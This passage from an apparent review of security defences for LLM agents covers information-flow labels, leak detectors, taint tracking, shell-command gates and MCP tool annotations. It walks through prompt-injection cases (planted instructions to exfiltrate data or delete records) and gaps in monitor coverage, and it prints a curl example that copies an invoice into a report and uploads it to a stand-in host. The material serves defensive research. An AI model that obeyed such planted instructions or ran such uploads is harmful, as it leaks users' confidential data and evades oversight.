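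The detector also over-marked, with a precision of 86.68%. About 6,800 of the fields it marked were ordinary, or roughly seven per task. Given the results on over-marking, that would probably be acceptable in exchange for fewer misses. But Ma and Schmid scored the detector on the inventory they had used for development and did not run the agents with its labels, so the audit does not show how well the detector handles unfamiliar records or how many leaks its misses would cause.

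The agents were run with a more conservative fallback that identifies protected fields from the schema (the formal description of a record's fields) alone. No protected value appeared in any of the three channels in all 996 scenarios, and the agents completed 85.9% of tasks. This is a good result, but it doesn't prove that the fallback marked every protected field, since most random misses didn't cause leaks either. Even if the scenarios are a fair sample, zero leaks in 496 attacked cases is statistically compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 0.7%.

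A schema-only rule also needs a schema that describes the data well. The benchmark's records have named fields with declared types, but Ana's invoices include a free-text note where a supplier may type its account number. A rule that works on whole fields would have to protect the entire note to protect the number.

The most important limit of these experiments is that the missed fields in the leakage test were random. An attacker who learns which names a detector overlooks, and who can influence how data arrives, can make it miss the most valuable field repeatedly. Results at a random 1% miss rate provide little evidence about such an attack. The choice of model is another limit. Ma and Schmid ran their main comparisons on GPT-4o mini, a small model from July 2024, and their AgentLeak check on Claude Sonnet 4 covered only 50 rows. They acknowledge that leakage in final answers depends on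 how the model writes.

### When an outsider infers the secret

A check for copied values misses anything that an outsider can infer. Mohammadi and colleagues measured this kind of inference in their study of agents that make tool calls before it is clear whether the calls are needed. They gave a second model, Claude Haiku 4.5, a record of what the outside services had received and had it guess which of 150 sensitive topics the user's task concerned. Random guessing would be correct about 0.7% of the time.

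They then changed sensitive labels to "public" at random and compared two defences. One rewrites sensitive arguments in general terms, and the other sends the request to a trusted local substitute. Each figure below comes from 150 tasks run three times.

| Sensitive labels changed to public | No protection | Rewriting | Local substitute |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 12.2% | 2.7% | 2.2% |
| 10% | 11.8% | 3.6% | 4.2% |
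| 20% | 11.6% | 5.8% | 7.8% |

The guesser had never succeeded against the local substitute when the labels were correct, but with a fifth of the sensitive labels missing, it succeeded about two-thirds as often as it did with no protection. The agents proposed about eight early calls per task, so most tasks probably contained at least one mislabelled call, and a single revealing search can be enough to identify the topic.

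Mohammadi and colleagues emphasise that both defences still beat the unprotected agent, so their ranking of the defences holds under plausible labelling errors. That is useful to someone choosing between designs, but a company that has promised its customers confidentiality needs to know the absolute level of protection. With these errors, the best defence went from no successful guesses to one in 13.

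### What agreement between labellers shows

Researchers who lack verified labels often compare one labeller with another. Mohammadi and colleagues compared the labelling rules in their prototype with labels from Claude Opus 4.7 on 394 tool calls, and they report accuracy and macro-F1. F1 combines precision, the share of a labeller's marks that are correct, with recall, the share of true cases it finds. Macro-F1 is the average of the F1 scores for each label, so a rare label counts as much as a common one.

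| What the rules label | Accuracy | Macro-F1 | Main disagreement with Opus 4.7 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Destination of the call | 73% | 0.59 | Addresses containing a scrambled user ID count as public, and routine document searches as personal |
| Arguments of the call | 31% | 0.10 | Every argument gets the same label, "intent-revealing", whatever it contains |
| Effect of the call | 81% | 0.45 | Reads that the outside service logs count as reads with no lasting effect |

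The prototype does not satisfy the label premise of their theorem, which by their own standard requires a macro-F1 of at least 0.9. They argue that their comparison of defences is still valid because every defence used the same labels.

However, the scores are a poor measure of danger. The argument rules scored worst, but "intent-revealing" is the most restrictive of their four possible labels, so they over-mark most arguments and never give a sensitive one too permissive a label. The destination rules scored much better, yet they label an address public when it contains a scrambled user ID, which may still identify a person. A single agreement score combines missed fields with over-marking, although the SecureClaw results suggest that these errors have very different consequences.

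In a second audit, *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) compared the labels that OpenAI's o1 model and human annotators separately gave to 80 tools from InjecAgent, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks. The paper's access-control system, SEAgent, gives each tool five labels, which record what the tool acts on, what kind of action it takes, how sensitive the action is, whether its output is personal, and whether its output is trustworthy.

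They measured agreement with Cohen's kappa,

κ = (pₒ − pₑ) / (1 − pₑ),

where pₒ is the observed agreement and pₑ is the agreement expected by chance. A kappa of 1 means perfect agreement and 0 means no better than chance. The overall figure was 0.95. For the separate labels it ranged from 1.00 for the object of the action to 0.77 for sensitivity, and the simple average of the five was 0.89. The overall figure is probably higher because pooling labels with different possible answers makes chance agreement less likely, which raises kappa.

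The model and the people agreed least on sensitivity, a label that controls whether several of SEAgent's rules apply. The rules against poisoned databases and untrusted agents cover only tools whose sensitivity is above "low". The model rated a tool that opens web pages "low", while the people rated it "moderate" because it could lead a user to a phishing site. With the model's label, those rules would never apply to the tool, and SEAgent allows any action that no rule forbids.

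A mismatch in names could have a similar effect. One of SEAgent's published rules tests an attribute called "integrality", but its published rule language defines "integrity". The reported results suggest that the working code handles this. However, in a system that allows actions by default, a rule that never matches produces no error.

Ji and colleagues recommend that people review and correct the labels a model produces, and did so for their own tests. With these labels, SEAgent stopped every attack in the InjecAgent and AgentDojo benchmarks. They asked how well the system defends "given proper labels", so the result is evidence about the rules and their enforcement.

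Agreement between reviewers is strong evidence of correct labels only if the reviewers tend to make different mistakes. Suppose two reviewers each overlook 5% of protected fields. If their errors are independent, they will both overlook only about 0.25% of the fields, and comparing their work will expose nearly all the misses. But if both rely on the same misleading document, they may agree on every label while overlooking the same 5%.

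Ji and colleagues gave the model and the people the same descriptions of each tool's function, inputs and outputs. In Ana's company, `export_pdf` is described as formatting an invoice, but it uploads the invoice to the public web. A model and a person reading that description would probably both label the tool as local and low in sensitivity, so they would agree perfectly even though both were wrong. Comparing the labels with what the tool actually does would be more informative, because that doesn't depend on the description.

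Some disagreements are about definitions. Opus 4.7 treated a search as changing outside state because the provider keeps a log of it, but the prototype's rules did not. Either choice can be reasonable, but the policy has to use the same definition as the labels. Similarly, the detector's 99.22% recall on AgentLeak is measured against the benchmark's privacy rules, and Ana's company might use different ones.

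### Labels lost inside the model

A field can enter the system with the right label and lose it later. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Tang and colleagues, 2026) describes three ways a tracker can lose the connection between a source and what the agent later does with it.

Paraphrasing can hide sensitive information from a tracker that looks for matching text. In one test case, a research agent reads a web page that contains a confidential patient note and a hidden instruction to include the note in polished language. The agent's memo reports the diagnosis and treatment in different words, so the tracker finds no match.

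In another case, the source changes a decision but leaves no text to match. An agent normally searches the web and then runs code on the results. An attacker plants a search result with an instruction to send all results to an outside address first, and the agent calls an upload tool instead. The body of the upload contains the agent's own research, and the attacker's text affects only the choice of tool and the destination.

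Data can also lose its label when an agent saves it to memory. For example, an agent might store a confidential revenue forecast in one session and retrieve it for a report in another. If the software saved the text without its label, the second session would treat the forecast as ordinary data. Ana's runtime could lose the label on an account number in the same way if it wrote the number to a shared memory that stores only text.

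Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint, an auditing tool that finds such connections after a run has finished. It first builds a graph of where each piece of data came from, including data that passed through memory. When the agent has made a sensitive call, NeuroTaint searches the call's arguments for text that resembles the source in wording or meaning. If it finds none, it checks whether the agent would still have made the call with the source removed or replaced by neutral text. If the decision changes, that is evidence that the source influenced the call.

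The NeuroTaint paper tests its system on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios built for the paper from 20 agent frameworks. NeuroTaint's precision was 0.921 and its recall 0.935, which gives an F1 of 0.928. The paper's version of FIDES, the labelling planner by Costa and colleagues, scored 0.522.

FIDES could still block the attacks it failed to trace in this comparison. Cai and colleagues describe it as following known paths between labelled tools, but in the design that Costa and colleagues published, every later tool call inherits the conversation's combined label. The planted search result would therefore make the upload call untrusted, even if the text was paraphrased or didn't match at all, and the integrity policy could refuse the call.

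This coverage makes the published design less precise. In the patient-note case, even the baseline flagged the path from the web page to the memo, but Cai and colleagues point out that the same rule would flag harmless research that follows that path. F1 penalises false alarms as well as misses, so a tracker can score low because it flags too much. The memory case is a more serious problem for both designs, because a label on a conversation doesn't protect data in the next session unless the software stores the label with the data.

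NeuroTaint analyses logs after the event, so it can identify a leak but cannot prevent it. It needs the model's intermediate reasoning as well as the record of tool calls, and someone has to declare which tools are sources and which are sinks. It missed about 6.5% of the real connections in a benchmark that its own designers built. They also exclude attacks hidden in images or in disguised characters.

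Each NeuroTaint label includes a confidence score between 0 and 1, whereas a conventional label is either present or absent. The score can indicate that a source probably had little influence on a call. A monitor still has to allow or refuse the call, so someone has to choose a threshold, and an attacker can try to stay below it. Scores allow the balance between misses and false alarms to be adjusted, but they can't provide the guarantee that comes from assuming every input influenced the output.

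### Labels that spread too far

The cautious assumption leads to the opposite failure, label explosion. In an example Ji and colleagues give from their own design, a user runs a web search in one round of conversation and asks for a photo in the next. If the system keeps the search result marked as untrusted and links it to everything that follows, it treats the photo request as an attack.

Clearing the record of sources between rounds would remove the false alarm, but it could also let an attack through. The search result might contain an instruction to grant access to the user's location at the next request. If the system deletes the record of where that text came from but leaves the text in the model's conversation, it won't flag the later call. SEAgent therefore clears both the record and the conversation after each round. A separate model then chooses which past messages and tool results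 the next round needs, and each is restored with the record of its source.

This memory keeps labels attached to their data, but the agent makes somewhat fewer correct tool calls. On API-Bank, a benchmark of everyday tool use, 73% of an unprotected agent's tool calls were correct, compared with 68% for SEAgent with this memory. On tasks that needed two tools, the share fell from 74% to 50%, although it rose on the other tasks. Ji and colleagues call the overall difference modest.

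RTBAS (Zhong et al., 2025) addresses the spread of labels more directly. It estimates which earlier parts of the conversation a tool call depends on and applies only their labels to the call. Ana can then read a supplier's untrusted note and still send an unrelated e-mail, provided the estimate is right. If the estimate omits a part that influenced the call, the call's label will be too permissive, as it would be if a detector had missed a field.

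Strict rules can appear to do little harm to task performance in tests where the refused actions are optional. Mohammadi and colleagues tried a policy that refuses every early call with a sensitive label, which reduced the calls reaching outside services from about eight per task to fewer than 0.5. In a separate test, a model judged the final answers about as good as before, because the agent could still make necessary calls later. An agent that cannot postpone a refused call would fail the task.

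Looser rules have the opposite weakness. Mohammadi and colleagues also tested a policy modelled on FIDES, which tracks each field and lets each destination accept certain kinds of sensitive data. Under this policy, the guesser identified the topic in 13.1% of trials, compared with 10.4% with no protection, a difference within the margin of error. Under two stricter tracking policies, the figure was between 7% and 8%. The looser policy failed to lower the figure because it allowed calls whose topic matched the destination, such as a medical question to a medical service, and the topic was what the guesser had to identify. Better labels would not have changed that result, because the policy permitted the disclosure.

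Pressure to reduce false alarms can also introduce new labelling errors. In Ji and colleagues' first test on API-Bank, SEAgent blocked only two legitimate tasks. In both, the agent had consulted Wikipedia, which the researchers had labelled untrusted, before trying to record health data or register an appointment. They suggest a real deployment could avoid the problem by labelling the Wikipedia tool as trusted. But anyone can edit Wikipedia, so an attacker's text could then lead to the same sensitive actions without triggering the rule that blocked these two tasks.

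## Experiments with tool effects the monitor does not control

Even perfect labels do not help when the monitor does not control a tool's effects. Developers may never have registered the tool, or may have registered it as harmless, as Ana's company did with `export_pdf`. A tool like `run_shell` may also be so general that approving one call approves many different effects. Researchers have tested parts of this problem by switching off checks, recording what supposedly harmless tools disclose, and running hostile shell scripts.

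### Tools the monitor never sees

A company's list of tools, drawn up before deployment, does not cover anything an agent may add while it runs. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes agents that write and register their own tools, start child processes and connect to remote services.

Zhang moves the check from the wrapper around `send_email` to the low-level operation that opens connections. A newly written tool that opens its own connection to the mail server would avoid a check in the wrapper, but it has to pass one at the lower level. A tool server that the company installs on the same machine still has to be trusted with whatever it does after receiving a request, because it runs as ordinary code under the host's account. Zhang also declares one exception, a read-only inspection of a Git repository that runs before the agent's authority to use it has been established.

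Ma and Schmid point out that checking a tool's arguments cannot substitute for controlling the tool itself when the tool takes no arguments. Suppose Ana's agent has a tool called `pay_approved()`, which pays every invoice in the approved queue. The call looks the same whether Ana or the supplier's note requested it, and whether the queue holds one invoice or a hundred, so an argument filter cannot distinguish these cases. The monitor could ban the tool outright, but to tell a proper call from an improper one, it needs information about who requested the call, in which session, and what is in the queue. It must also control the only route to the payment system, because otherwise the runtime can bypass the filter.

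In a small payment case study, Ma and Schmid tested SecureClaw with and without its executor's approval check. They raised a payment from $100 to $10,000, redirected another to an attacker, forged an approval and repeated an earlier payment. With the check on, all four attempts failed and a legitimate payment went through. With it off, all five payments went through. Though unsurprising, the result shows that nothing else in the system would have stopped the four attacks.

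### Removing half of SecureClaw

Ma and Schmid also ran an ablation, an experiment that removes parts of a system to see what each contributes. They ran 24 attacked and 24 ordinary scenarios from AgentLeak with and without SecureClaw's two main protections, the reference IDs and the executor's check on actions.

| Configuration | Attacked: leaks in agent messages | Attacked: leaks in shared memory | Ordinary: any leak |
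|---|---|---|---|
| Both protections | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 |
| No action check | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 |
| No reference IDs | 5 of 24 | 2 of 24 | 4 of 24 |
| Neither | 6 of 24 | 1 of 24 | 4 of 24 |

Removing the reference IDs reopened the leaks, while removing the action check did not. The action check cannot stop messages between agents because they never reach the executor. The reference IDs prevent leaks because a runtime that has never held the account number cannot pass it on. The leaks in ordinary scenarios also show that agents spread protected data internally even without an attacker.

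The ablation counted leaks but not the unauthorised payments or e-mails that the action check exists to prevent, so it does not show that the check is dispensable. The evidence for the check comes from the payment cases and a separate set of attacks on the executor.

The numbers are also very small. If the reference IDs made no difference, a gap at least as wide as five leaks to none would arise by chance about 5% of the time by Fisher's exact test. For two leaks to none, the figure is nearly 50%. Zero leaks in 24 scenarios is compatible with a true rate of up to about 14%, and the differences between the last two rows of the table are not meaningful. Ma and Schmid say that the sample limits the precision of the rates for each channel. The sample is also not typical of the benchmark, since an unprotected agent leaked through messages in 93% of the full set of attacked scenarios, against 25%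 here with both protections off. The ablation is best read as a check that each part has the effect it was designed to have, not as an estimate of how often a deployed system would leak.

A company is more likely to overlook one or two tools than to leave out the whole action check, but the ablation does not test for overlooked tools. Ma and Schmid varied the share of missed fields from 1% to 20%, but they report no matching experiment that leaves a controlled share of tools outside the executor. The results for missed fields are a poor guide to the effect of missed tools. A missed field leaks only if the runtime passes it on, which an ordinary model often doesn't do, whereas an attacker who controls the runtime can look for the one tool that skips the check and use it every time. Which tools the company overlooked would therefore matter more than how many, and an experiment that removed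 tools at random could understate the danger.

On Agent Security Bench, whose attacks use text planted in an agent's prompt to try to redirect its actions, SecureClaw stopped all 2,000 attacks on each of five models. Three of those models were also tested without a defence, and between 50% and 85% of the attacks on them succeeded. This is strong evidence that SecureClaw's check does not depend on which model proposes the action. However, the executor was in place in every run, so the results don't show what happens when a tool bypasses it.

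### Controlling actions but not reads

Faramesh, a system that Amjad Fatmi designed, checks an agent's actions before they run but leaves the data in the runtime alone. Ma and Schmid compared it with SecureClaw and an unprotected agent.

| Measure | No defence | Faramesh | SecureClaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attack success, Agent Security Bench | 91.65% | 0% | 0% |
| Tasks completed under attack, same benchmark | 0.85% | 3.70% | 88.90% |
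| Attack success, AgentDojo | 31.48% | 22.89% | 0.64% |
| Leaks through agent messages, AgentLeak | 92.74% | 92.74% | 0.20% |
| Leaks through shared memory, AgentLeak | 51.61% | 51.61% | 0% |

Faramesh stopped every attack on Agent Security Bench, but its leak rates inside the system match the unprotected agent's to the last digit, which suggests that it never intervened in those scenarios. A monitor tested only with attacks on outside actions could therefore get a perfect score even if it let agents copy account numbers to one another.

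The comparison is less informative about Faramesh as a product. Ma and Schmid kept its core unchanged but wrote the policies and the code connecting it to the benchmarks, so the AgentDojo result in particular may reflect those policies. Its perfect score of 0% on Agent Security Bench came with very few completed tasks, and a monitor that refused everything would score the same. However, the unprotected agent completed even fewer tasks, so refusals can't fully explain the low completion rate. Some of SecureClaw's lead in completed tasks comes from a separate feature that suggests a safe next step after a refusal. In a 50-case test, turning it on raised completion from 70% to 86%.

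### Why a read-only tool can still disclose information

A tool that only reads can still reveal information about a user through its queries, although developers often register such tools as harmless. Mohammadi and colleagues give the example of a tenant who asks an agent about the penalty for ending a lease early. The agent searches for tenancy law and, to save time, also looks up available flats and personal loan rates in case it needs them later. The answer uses only the search on tenancy law. None of the calls changes the tenant's files or accounts, but outside companies now hold records suggesting that someone wants to move out and may be short of money.

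"Read-only" means only that a call leaves the task's data unchanged. A read-only call to a tool that queries an outside service still sends data to that service in the query.

To measure the disclosure, Mohammadi and colleagues wrote 30 tasks, each with a sensitive topic, and decided in advance which calls the agent would finally use. They ran the tasks with and without extra early calls. As in the tests with wrong labels, a second model guessed the topic from the services' records, but this time it was Claude Opus 4.7, working from a list of 30 topics. They repeated the test with a model making the plans, and again on 150 tasks, giving every policy the same recorded set of proposed calls. The table gives the share of topics that the guesser identified.

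| Policy for early calls | 30 tasks, fixed plans | 30 tasks, model's plans | 150 tasks, replayed calls |
|---|---|---|---|
| No early calls | 44% | 34% | 8.0% |
| All allowed | 97% | 49% | 10.4% |
| Read-only tools only | 97% | 49% | 12.4% |
| Tools on an allow-list | 97% | 49% | 10.4% |
| Sensitive arguments rewritten | 53% | 4% | 2.9% |
| Trusted local substitute | 42% | 0% | 0% |

With fixed plans, the rise from 44% to 97% must come from the extra calls, because everything else stayed the same. Restricting the agent to read-only tools did not help, because searches are read-only, and neither did the allow-list, because it included the search tools. Removing sensitive text after the agent had settled on a plan also left the figure at 97%, because the services had already received the requests.

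The size of the jump depends heavily on the set-up. When a model made the plans, the jump shrank to 15 percentage points, with overlapping margins of error. In the replay, it shrank to about two points and fell just short of statistical significance. The replay did not hold the final plan constant, and the guesser had 150 topics to choose from. The 97% figure is therefore a measure of how much early calls can reveal under conditions built to isolate them, and everyday figures could be far lower. Neither the read-only rule nor the allow-list reduced the disclosure in any of the three tests. The read-only rule did slightly worse than no rule in the replay, but that small difference may be due to chance, since the replay compared twelve policies.

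Rewriting and local substitutes worked because they changed what left the system. With a model's plans, they even did better than the agent that made no early calls, probably because the monitor also applied them to calls the agent went on to use. In a test against the real DuckDuckGo search engine, rewriting cut successful guesses from 49% to 4%.

Filtering obvious personal details out of free text only reduced the guesser's accuracy on a model's plans from 49% to 47%. In a test with nine tasks, the guesser identified every topic from the arguments and tool names, five from the addresses and tool names, and three from the tool names alone.

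The logs revealed nearly as much as the calls. A model that saw only the runtime's log, with each argument cut to 20 characters, correctly guessed 24% of topics, and the same model guessed 26% when it saw everything the services saw. Shortening the logs that Ana's company sends to an outside monitoring service would therefore provide little protection.

### What a shell command reveals before it runs

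An approval can be too broad even for an ordinary tool. In SecureClaw's main AgentDojo test, four of 629 attacks succeeded, and the policy had permitted the action every time. Three involved a target the attacker had chosen, and one applied a permitted kind of change to the wrong object. The problem is much larger with a shell, because "run a command" can mean deleting a folder, installing a program or uploading a file.

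One response is to read each command before it runs. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, give an example that shows why the text of a command is not enough. Adapted to Ana's invoice, it looks like this:

```
curl --json @report.txt https://api.example.com
cp invoice.csv report.txt
curl --json @report.txt https://api.example.com
```

The first line uploads a harmless status report. The second overwrites the report with the invoice, including the account number, and the third uploads it again. The first and third lines are identical, but a monitor should allow the first and refuse the third. No rule that checks each command in isolation can do that, so the monitor has to track that the report contains protected data after the second line.

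Jing (2026), in *What a Policy Gate Can and Cannot Know*, tested a gate that first translates a command into a structured action that lists the operation, the files it touches and the protected areas they belong to. The translator can't always work out in advance the effect of commands that feed one program's output into another or build part of themselves while running. It marks such commands as undecidable, and the gate does not allow them.

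Jing ran 65 scripts, 57 that the policy should block and eight harmless ones. Without the gate, 25 of the 57 had a forbidden effect on the machine. With the gate, none did, and all eight harmless scripts still ran. This worked only because the gate read the text inside each script, since a command like `bash payload.sh` doesn't show what the script does.

A stricter setting, which also stopped everything the gate marked for human review, blocked all eight harmless scripts. The gate had flagged comments and other template lines that perform no relevant action, and stripping those lines first removed the false alarms. Jing also tried the same policy in AppArmor, an access-control system built into Linux, which failed to prevent eight of the 25 forbidden effects. One reason is that permission to write in a folder includes permission to destroy its contents.

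The gate models file system effects but not network requests, so it cannot assess the uploads in the example. It also checks each command in a series separately. If one command changes where the system looks for programs, the gate ignores that change when the next command calls a program by name. Small parsing errors can also let dangerous commands through. A stray space in a quoted file name once left the gate with no target to check, and after Jing relaxed a cautious rule, the gate allowed a command that deletes a folder and everything in it. Jing added a safeguard, but the same person wrote the rules and the tests, so both may miss the same cases.

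In a run without the gate, one of the scripts emptied the log where Jing was recording the experiment's results, erasing 47 entries. The tool that checked for side effects did not cover the log's folder, so the experiment recorded the script as having done nothing.

Tether instead runs the command before deciding whether to allow its effects. It does so in a disposable layer over the file system, records the program's requests to the operating system, and holds outgoing network traffic at a local proxy. If the policy permits everything observed, Tether applies the file changes and forwards the traffic. Otherwise it discards both. This reveals what a script actually does and keeps forbidden requests from leaving the machine. Permitted requests are still sent, so Tether would not by itself prevent the disclosures that Mohammadi and colleagues measured, which came from searches and lookups that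 the policy allowed. Tether keeps labels between commands, so it allows the first upload in the example, marks the report as sensitive after the copy, and refuses the second upload.

Tether cannot detect exactly which bytes a program copied, so if a program reads a protected file and then writes another, Tether treats this as a transfer of protected data. This causes some false alarms. Sistla and colleagues report that, on two benchmarks of coding agents, Tether blocked every attack within its scope and raised false alarms on 2.3% and 5.0% of harmless runs.

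"Within its scope" limits the result to runs in which Tether could trace every action, so the perfect score assumes complete mediation. Some of the excluded runs worked through databases or background services, whose internal behaviour Tether cannot follow. It can detect and block contact with such a service, but Ana's agent may need the company's database to do its job. Other excluded attacks broke no rule about data or privileges, so better tracing would not have caught them. Sistla and colleagues have proofs about how Tether's policies behave, but those proofs start from the list of effects that the tracer reports. Tether cannot apply a policy to an upload that the tracer misses.

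## Surveys of tools and agent software in use

Tether traces a tool's effects while the tool runs. A company that does not do this has to rely on what the tool's author declares. Surveys of published software measure how often authors omit these declarations and, less reliably, how often the declarations are wrong.

### Hints in the Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which Anthropic introduced in late 2024, is now a common way to connect agents to tools. An MCP server offers tools, each with a name, a plain-language description and a schema for its arguments. The host is the application the user works in, such as a chat program or a coding assistant. It runs the model, gives it the tool descriptions and forwards the tool calls the model proposes. Afsar (2026), in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, counted 24,135 servers in the official registry in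 August 2026, up from 16,548 less than six weeks earlier.

Since March 2025, a tool's author has been able to add four true-or-false annotations about its behaviour.

| Annotation | Meaning if true | Value assumed if missing |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool does not modify its environment | false |
| `destructiveHint` | Its changes may destroy something, not just add to it | true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments is safe | false |
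| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with outside parties or systems | true |

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) does not compare a tool's annotations with its code. The MCP project explains in a post that the specification calls all four annotations "hints" and requires clients to treat them as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. During the original review, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked how a client could use a flag it could not trust. The compromise was to let each client decide how much weight to give the hints. For anything that needs a guarantee, the post recommends network controls or sandboxing, which confines a program to a restricted environment.

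The hints also contain far less information than a system like FIDES needs. They cannot specify that `export_pdf` reads the account number or who can open the finished file. A draft proposal by GitHub and OpenAI would add annotations for trust and sensitivity.

### How many tools carry annotations

Afsar randomly sampled 400 servers from those in the registry that run locally as packages from the npm software repository. Only 195 started and completed the opening exchange with the test program. They offered 2,766 tools, of which 58.8% had no annotations. Of the servers with at least one tool, 72 had annotations on every tool and 122 had none, so a company that connects an unannotated server usually adds a whole set of unannotated tools at once.

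In a hand-picked set of reference and popular servers, only 41.5% of tools lacked annotations, so surveys of well-known servers overstate coverage. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) reports much lower coverage in another sample, with annotations on 325 of 1,856 tools, or about 18%.

*When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (2026), a census of 98,291 tools on remote servers, concludes that the presence of an annotation field is weak evidence that anyone chose its value. Of these tools, 52.8% were marked read-only and also had a value for `destructiveHint`, which has no meaning for a read-only tool. Excluding one dominant publisher lowered the share to 26.0%.

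### Descriptions compared with code

Checking whether a declaration is true requires knowing what the code does. Li, Ma and colleagues (2026), in *Don’t believe everything you read*, tried to automate this for 10,240 MCP servers with a program called MCPDiFF, which examines the servers' documentation rather than their annotations.

MCPDiFF analyses the source code without running it. It maps which functions call which, treats every function that no other function calls as an entry point, and follows the calls from there. A language model summarises what each chain of calls does and lists the features described in files such as the README and the manifest. MCPDiFF converts the summaries and the listed features into vectors to measure how similar they are in meaning, and checks whether the documentation covers each feature in the code. It ignores features that the documentation describes but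 the code lacks, because Li and colleagues were looking for hidden behaviour.

| Agreement between documentation and code | Servers | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Full | 5,303 | 51.8% |
| 80% to 100% | 3,544 | 34.6% |
| 40% to 80% | 1,079 | 10.5% |
| Below 40% | 314 | 3.1% |

The study's headline figure of about 13% combines the last two rows, which contain 1,393 servers. It counts servers with a lot of undocumented functionality, whether or not that functionality is harmful. A server could be included because its README omits several date-formatting functions, while a server that documented nine of its ten features but omitted an upload to the public web would score 90% and be excluded.

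Li and colleagues describe three servers with undeclared side effects but do not report how many of the 1,393 have them. The development framework mcpx-py contains an undocumented function that can terminate any process and every process it started. The documentation for longport-mcp, which connects to a trading service, omits the functions that submit and cancel orders. The third server, zerops-mcp, is advertised as offering read-only access to GitHub but has a function that changes user information.

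Even these cases do not show that an attacker could have exploited the mismatch. A function MCPDiFF treats as an entry point may be a helper that the server never offers as a tool. The description a server sends to the model can also be more accurate than its README. Demonstrating an exploit would require running the server and getting an agent to cause the hidden effect, and Li and colleagues describe no such test.

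They also report no error rate for MCPDiFF, and no sample of its results that people checked by hand. Because most servers appear consistent, even a modest rate of false alarms would change the estimate considerably. Let p be the true share of mismatched servers and f the share of consistent servers that MCPDiFF wrongly flags. If it catches every real mismatch, then

p + f(1 − p) = 0.136.

With f at 5%, the true share would be about 9%, and with f at 10%, about 4%. Missed mismatches would raise the estimate. Afsar cites a separate study of MCP security scanners in which manual checking confirmed fewer than half of a sample of alerts. Those scanners are different programs, but their error rate is a good reason to want validation here.

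Popularity did not reliably indicate accurate documentation. None of the 19 servers with at least 10,000 GitHub stars fell below 40% agreement, but five were in the 40% to 80% group. Where a server was listed made more difference. On the marketplace mcpmarket, 22% of servers were in the bottom two groups, compared with 11% on mcp_world.

In *When Neither Side Confirms*, Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026) provide better evidence about wrong annotations. They sampled 1,000 repositories from the MCP registry and looked for destructive tools, defined as those that can irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send messages, move money or run arbitrary commands. Two language models separately judged 366 tools a rule-based program had flagged, and a third settled their disagreements. Using a weighted estimate, they found that about 5% of the destructive tools the program flagged were annotated as read-only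 or non-destructive and had no confirmation step on the server. Including tools the program had overlooked raised the figure to at least 10.6%.

Human reviewers rechecked 60 of the tools and agreed with the models about destructiveness on 51 of the 56 they were sure about. The models had called the other five destructive, but the reviewers judged their actions reversible or harmless. Some of the annotations counted as wrong may also be correct by MCP's definition, because a tool that sends a message adds something without destroying anything.

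### Defaults for an unlabelled tool

Under MCP's defaults, a host should assume that a tool without annotations may write, destroy data and reach outside parties. Most hosts do not act on that assumption. Yao and colleagues traced an ordinary tool call through the source code of 41 open-source hosts, including software kits for building agents. Seven asked the user before ordinary calls, and 32 had no approval step by default. One used a language model to decide, and only OpenAI's coding agent Codex CLI based its decision on the annotations. In the first two groups, 39 hosts in total, marking a tool destructive did not change how the host handled the call.

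Yao and colleagues also ran a test server with a tool for deleting notes. Using four of the software kits, they had five low-cost models read a list of notes containing a planted instruction to delete tax records. When the tool was annotated as destructive but had no other protection, all 180 deletions the models attempted went through.

Some server developers rely on the host to check destructive calls. Yao and colleagues estimate that 90% of destructive tools have no confirmation step on the server. The developers of one mapping server turned off its confirmation step by default, reasoning that hosts already check such calls.

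ToolUniverse, a library of scientific tools, makes the opposite assumption. Zitnik Lab's *Source code for tooluniverse.tool_defaults* sets every tool to read-only and non-destructive unless a more specific rule applies, because, according to a comment in the code, most of the tools are read-only database queries. Tools that combine other tools and tools that execute Python code are exceptions, and a developer can override the default for any single tool.

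This default is probably right for most of the library. But if a developer forgets to mark a tool that writes data, the tool receives the same explicit "read-only" label as a query that someone has reviewed, and a host cannot distinguish the unchecked label from the reviewed one.

Microsoft's Agent Framework includes an experimental version of FIDES, which treats unlabelled tool output as untrusted and public by default. Microsoft says that a tool the developer forgot to annotate therefore "fails closed rather than open", which is true for integrity because untrusted output can block later actions. But for confidentiality, "public" is the most permissive label, so if an unlabelled tool returned an account number, the framework would let that number go anywhere that accepts public data. According to the documentation, unlabelled output also inherits the combined label of the tool's inputs,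 so a developer would need to test which rule applies.

These labels describe what a tool returns. To limit when a tool may run, the developer must separately declare that it does not accept untrusted data, or that it accepts data only up to a given confidentiality level. In Microsoft's example, a file-reading tool has neither declaration and runs even after the agent has read a hostile message.

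Suppose Ana's company had left `export_pdf` unlabelled, instead of registering it as a harmless formatting tool.

| Default | What the system assumes | What happens |
|---|---|---|
| MCP, with a host that acts on the default | The tool may write and reach outside parties | Ana sees a prompt before the upload |
| MCP, with a host that has no approval step | The same, but nothing uses the assumption | The upload goes ahead |
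| ToolUniverse | The tool is read-only and non-destructive | A host that trusts the label runs it without asking |
| Agent Framework with FIDES | The returned link is untrusted and public | The upload goes ahead |

Only the first case gives anyone a chance to stop the leak, but Ana would probably approve a request to export a PDF. In the last case, the framework might later refuse to e-mail the link to Ben because the link is untrusted, but by then the account number would already be on the public web. The developers could have prevented this by declaring that `export_pdf` accepts only public data, if the supplier name and amount in the conversation carried a private label. Developers who believe the tool only formats pages have no reason to add that declaration. None of these defaults would have corrected the company's original wrong label.

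Hosts could follow MCP's default more strictly by prompting the user about every tool not annotated as read-only or non-destructive. Yao and colleagues paired the destructive tools in their sample with 25 applications and found no enforced approval in 60.7% of the pairs. The stricter rule would reduce that share to 5.4%. But among flagged tools that turned out not to be destructive, the share of pairs in which the user has to answer a prompt would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%.

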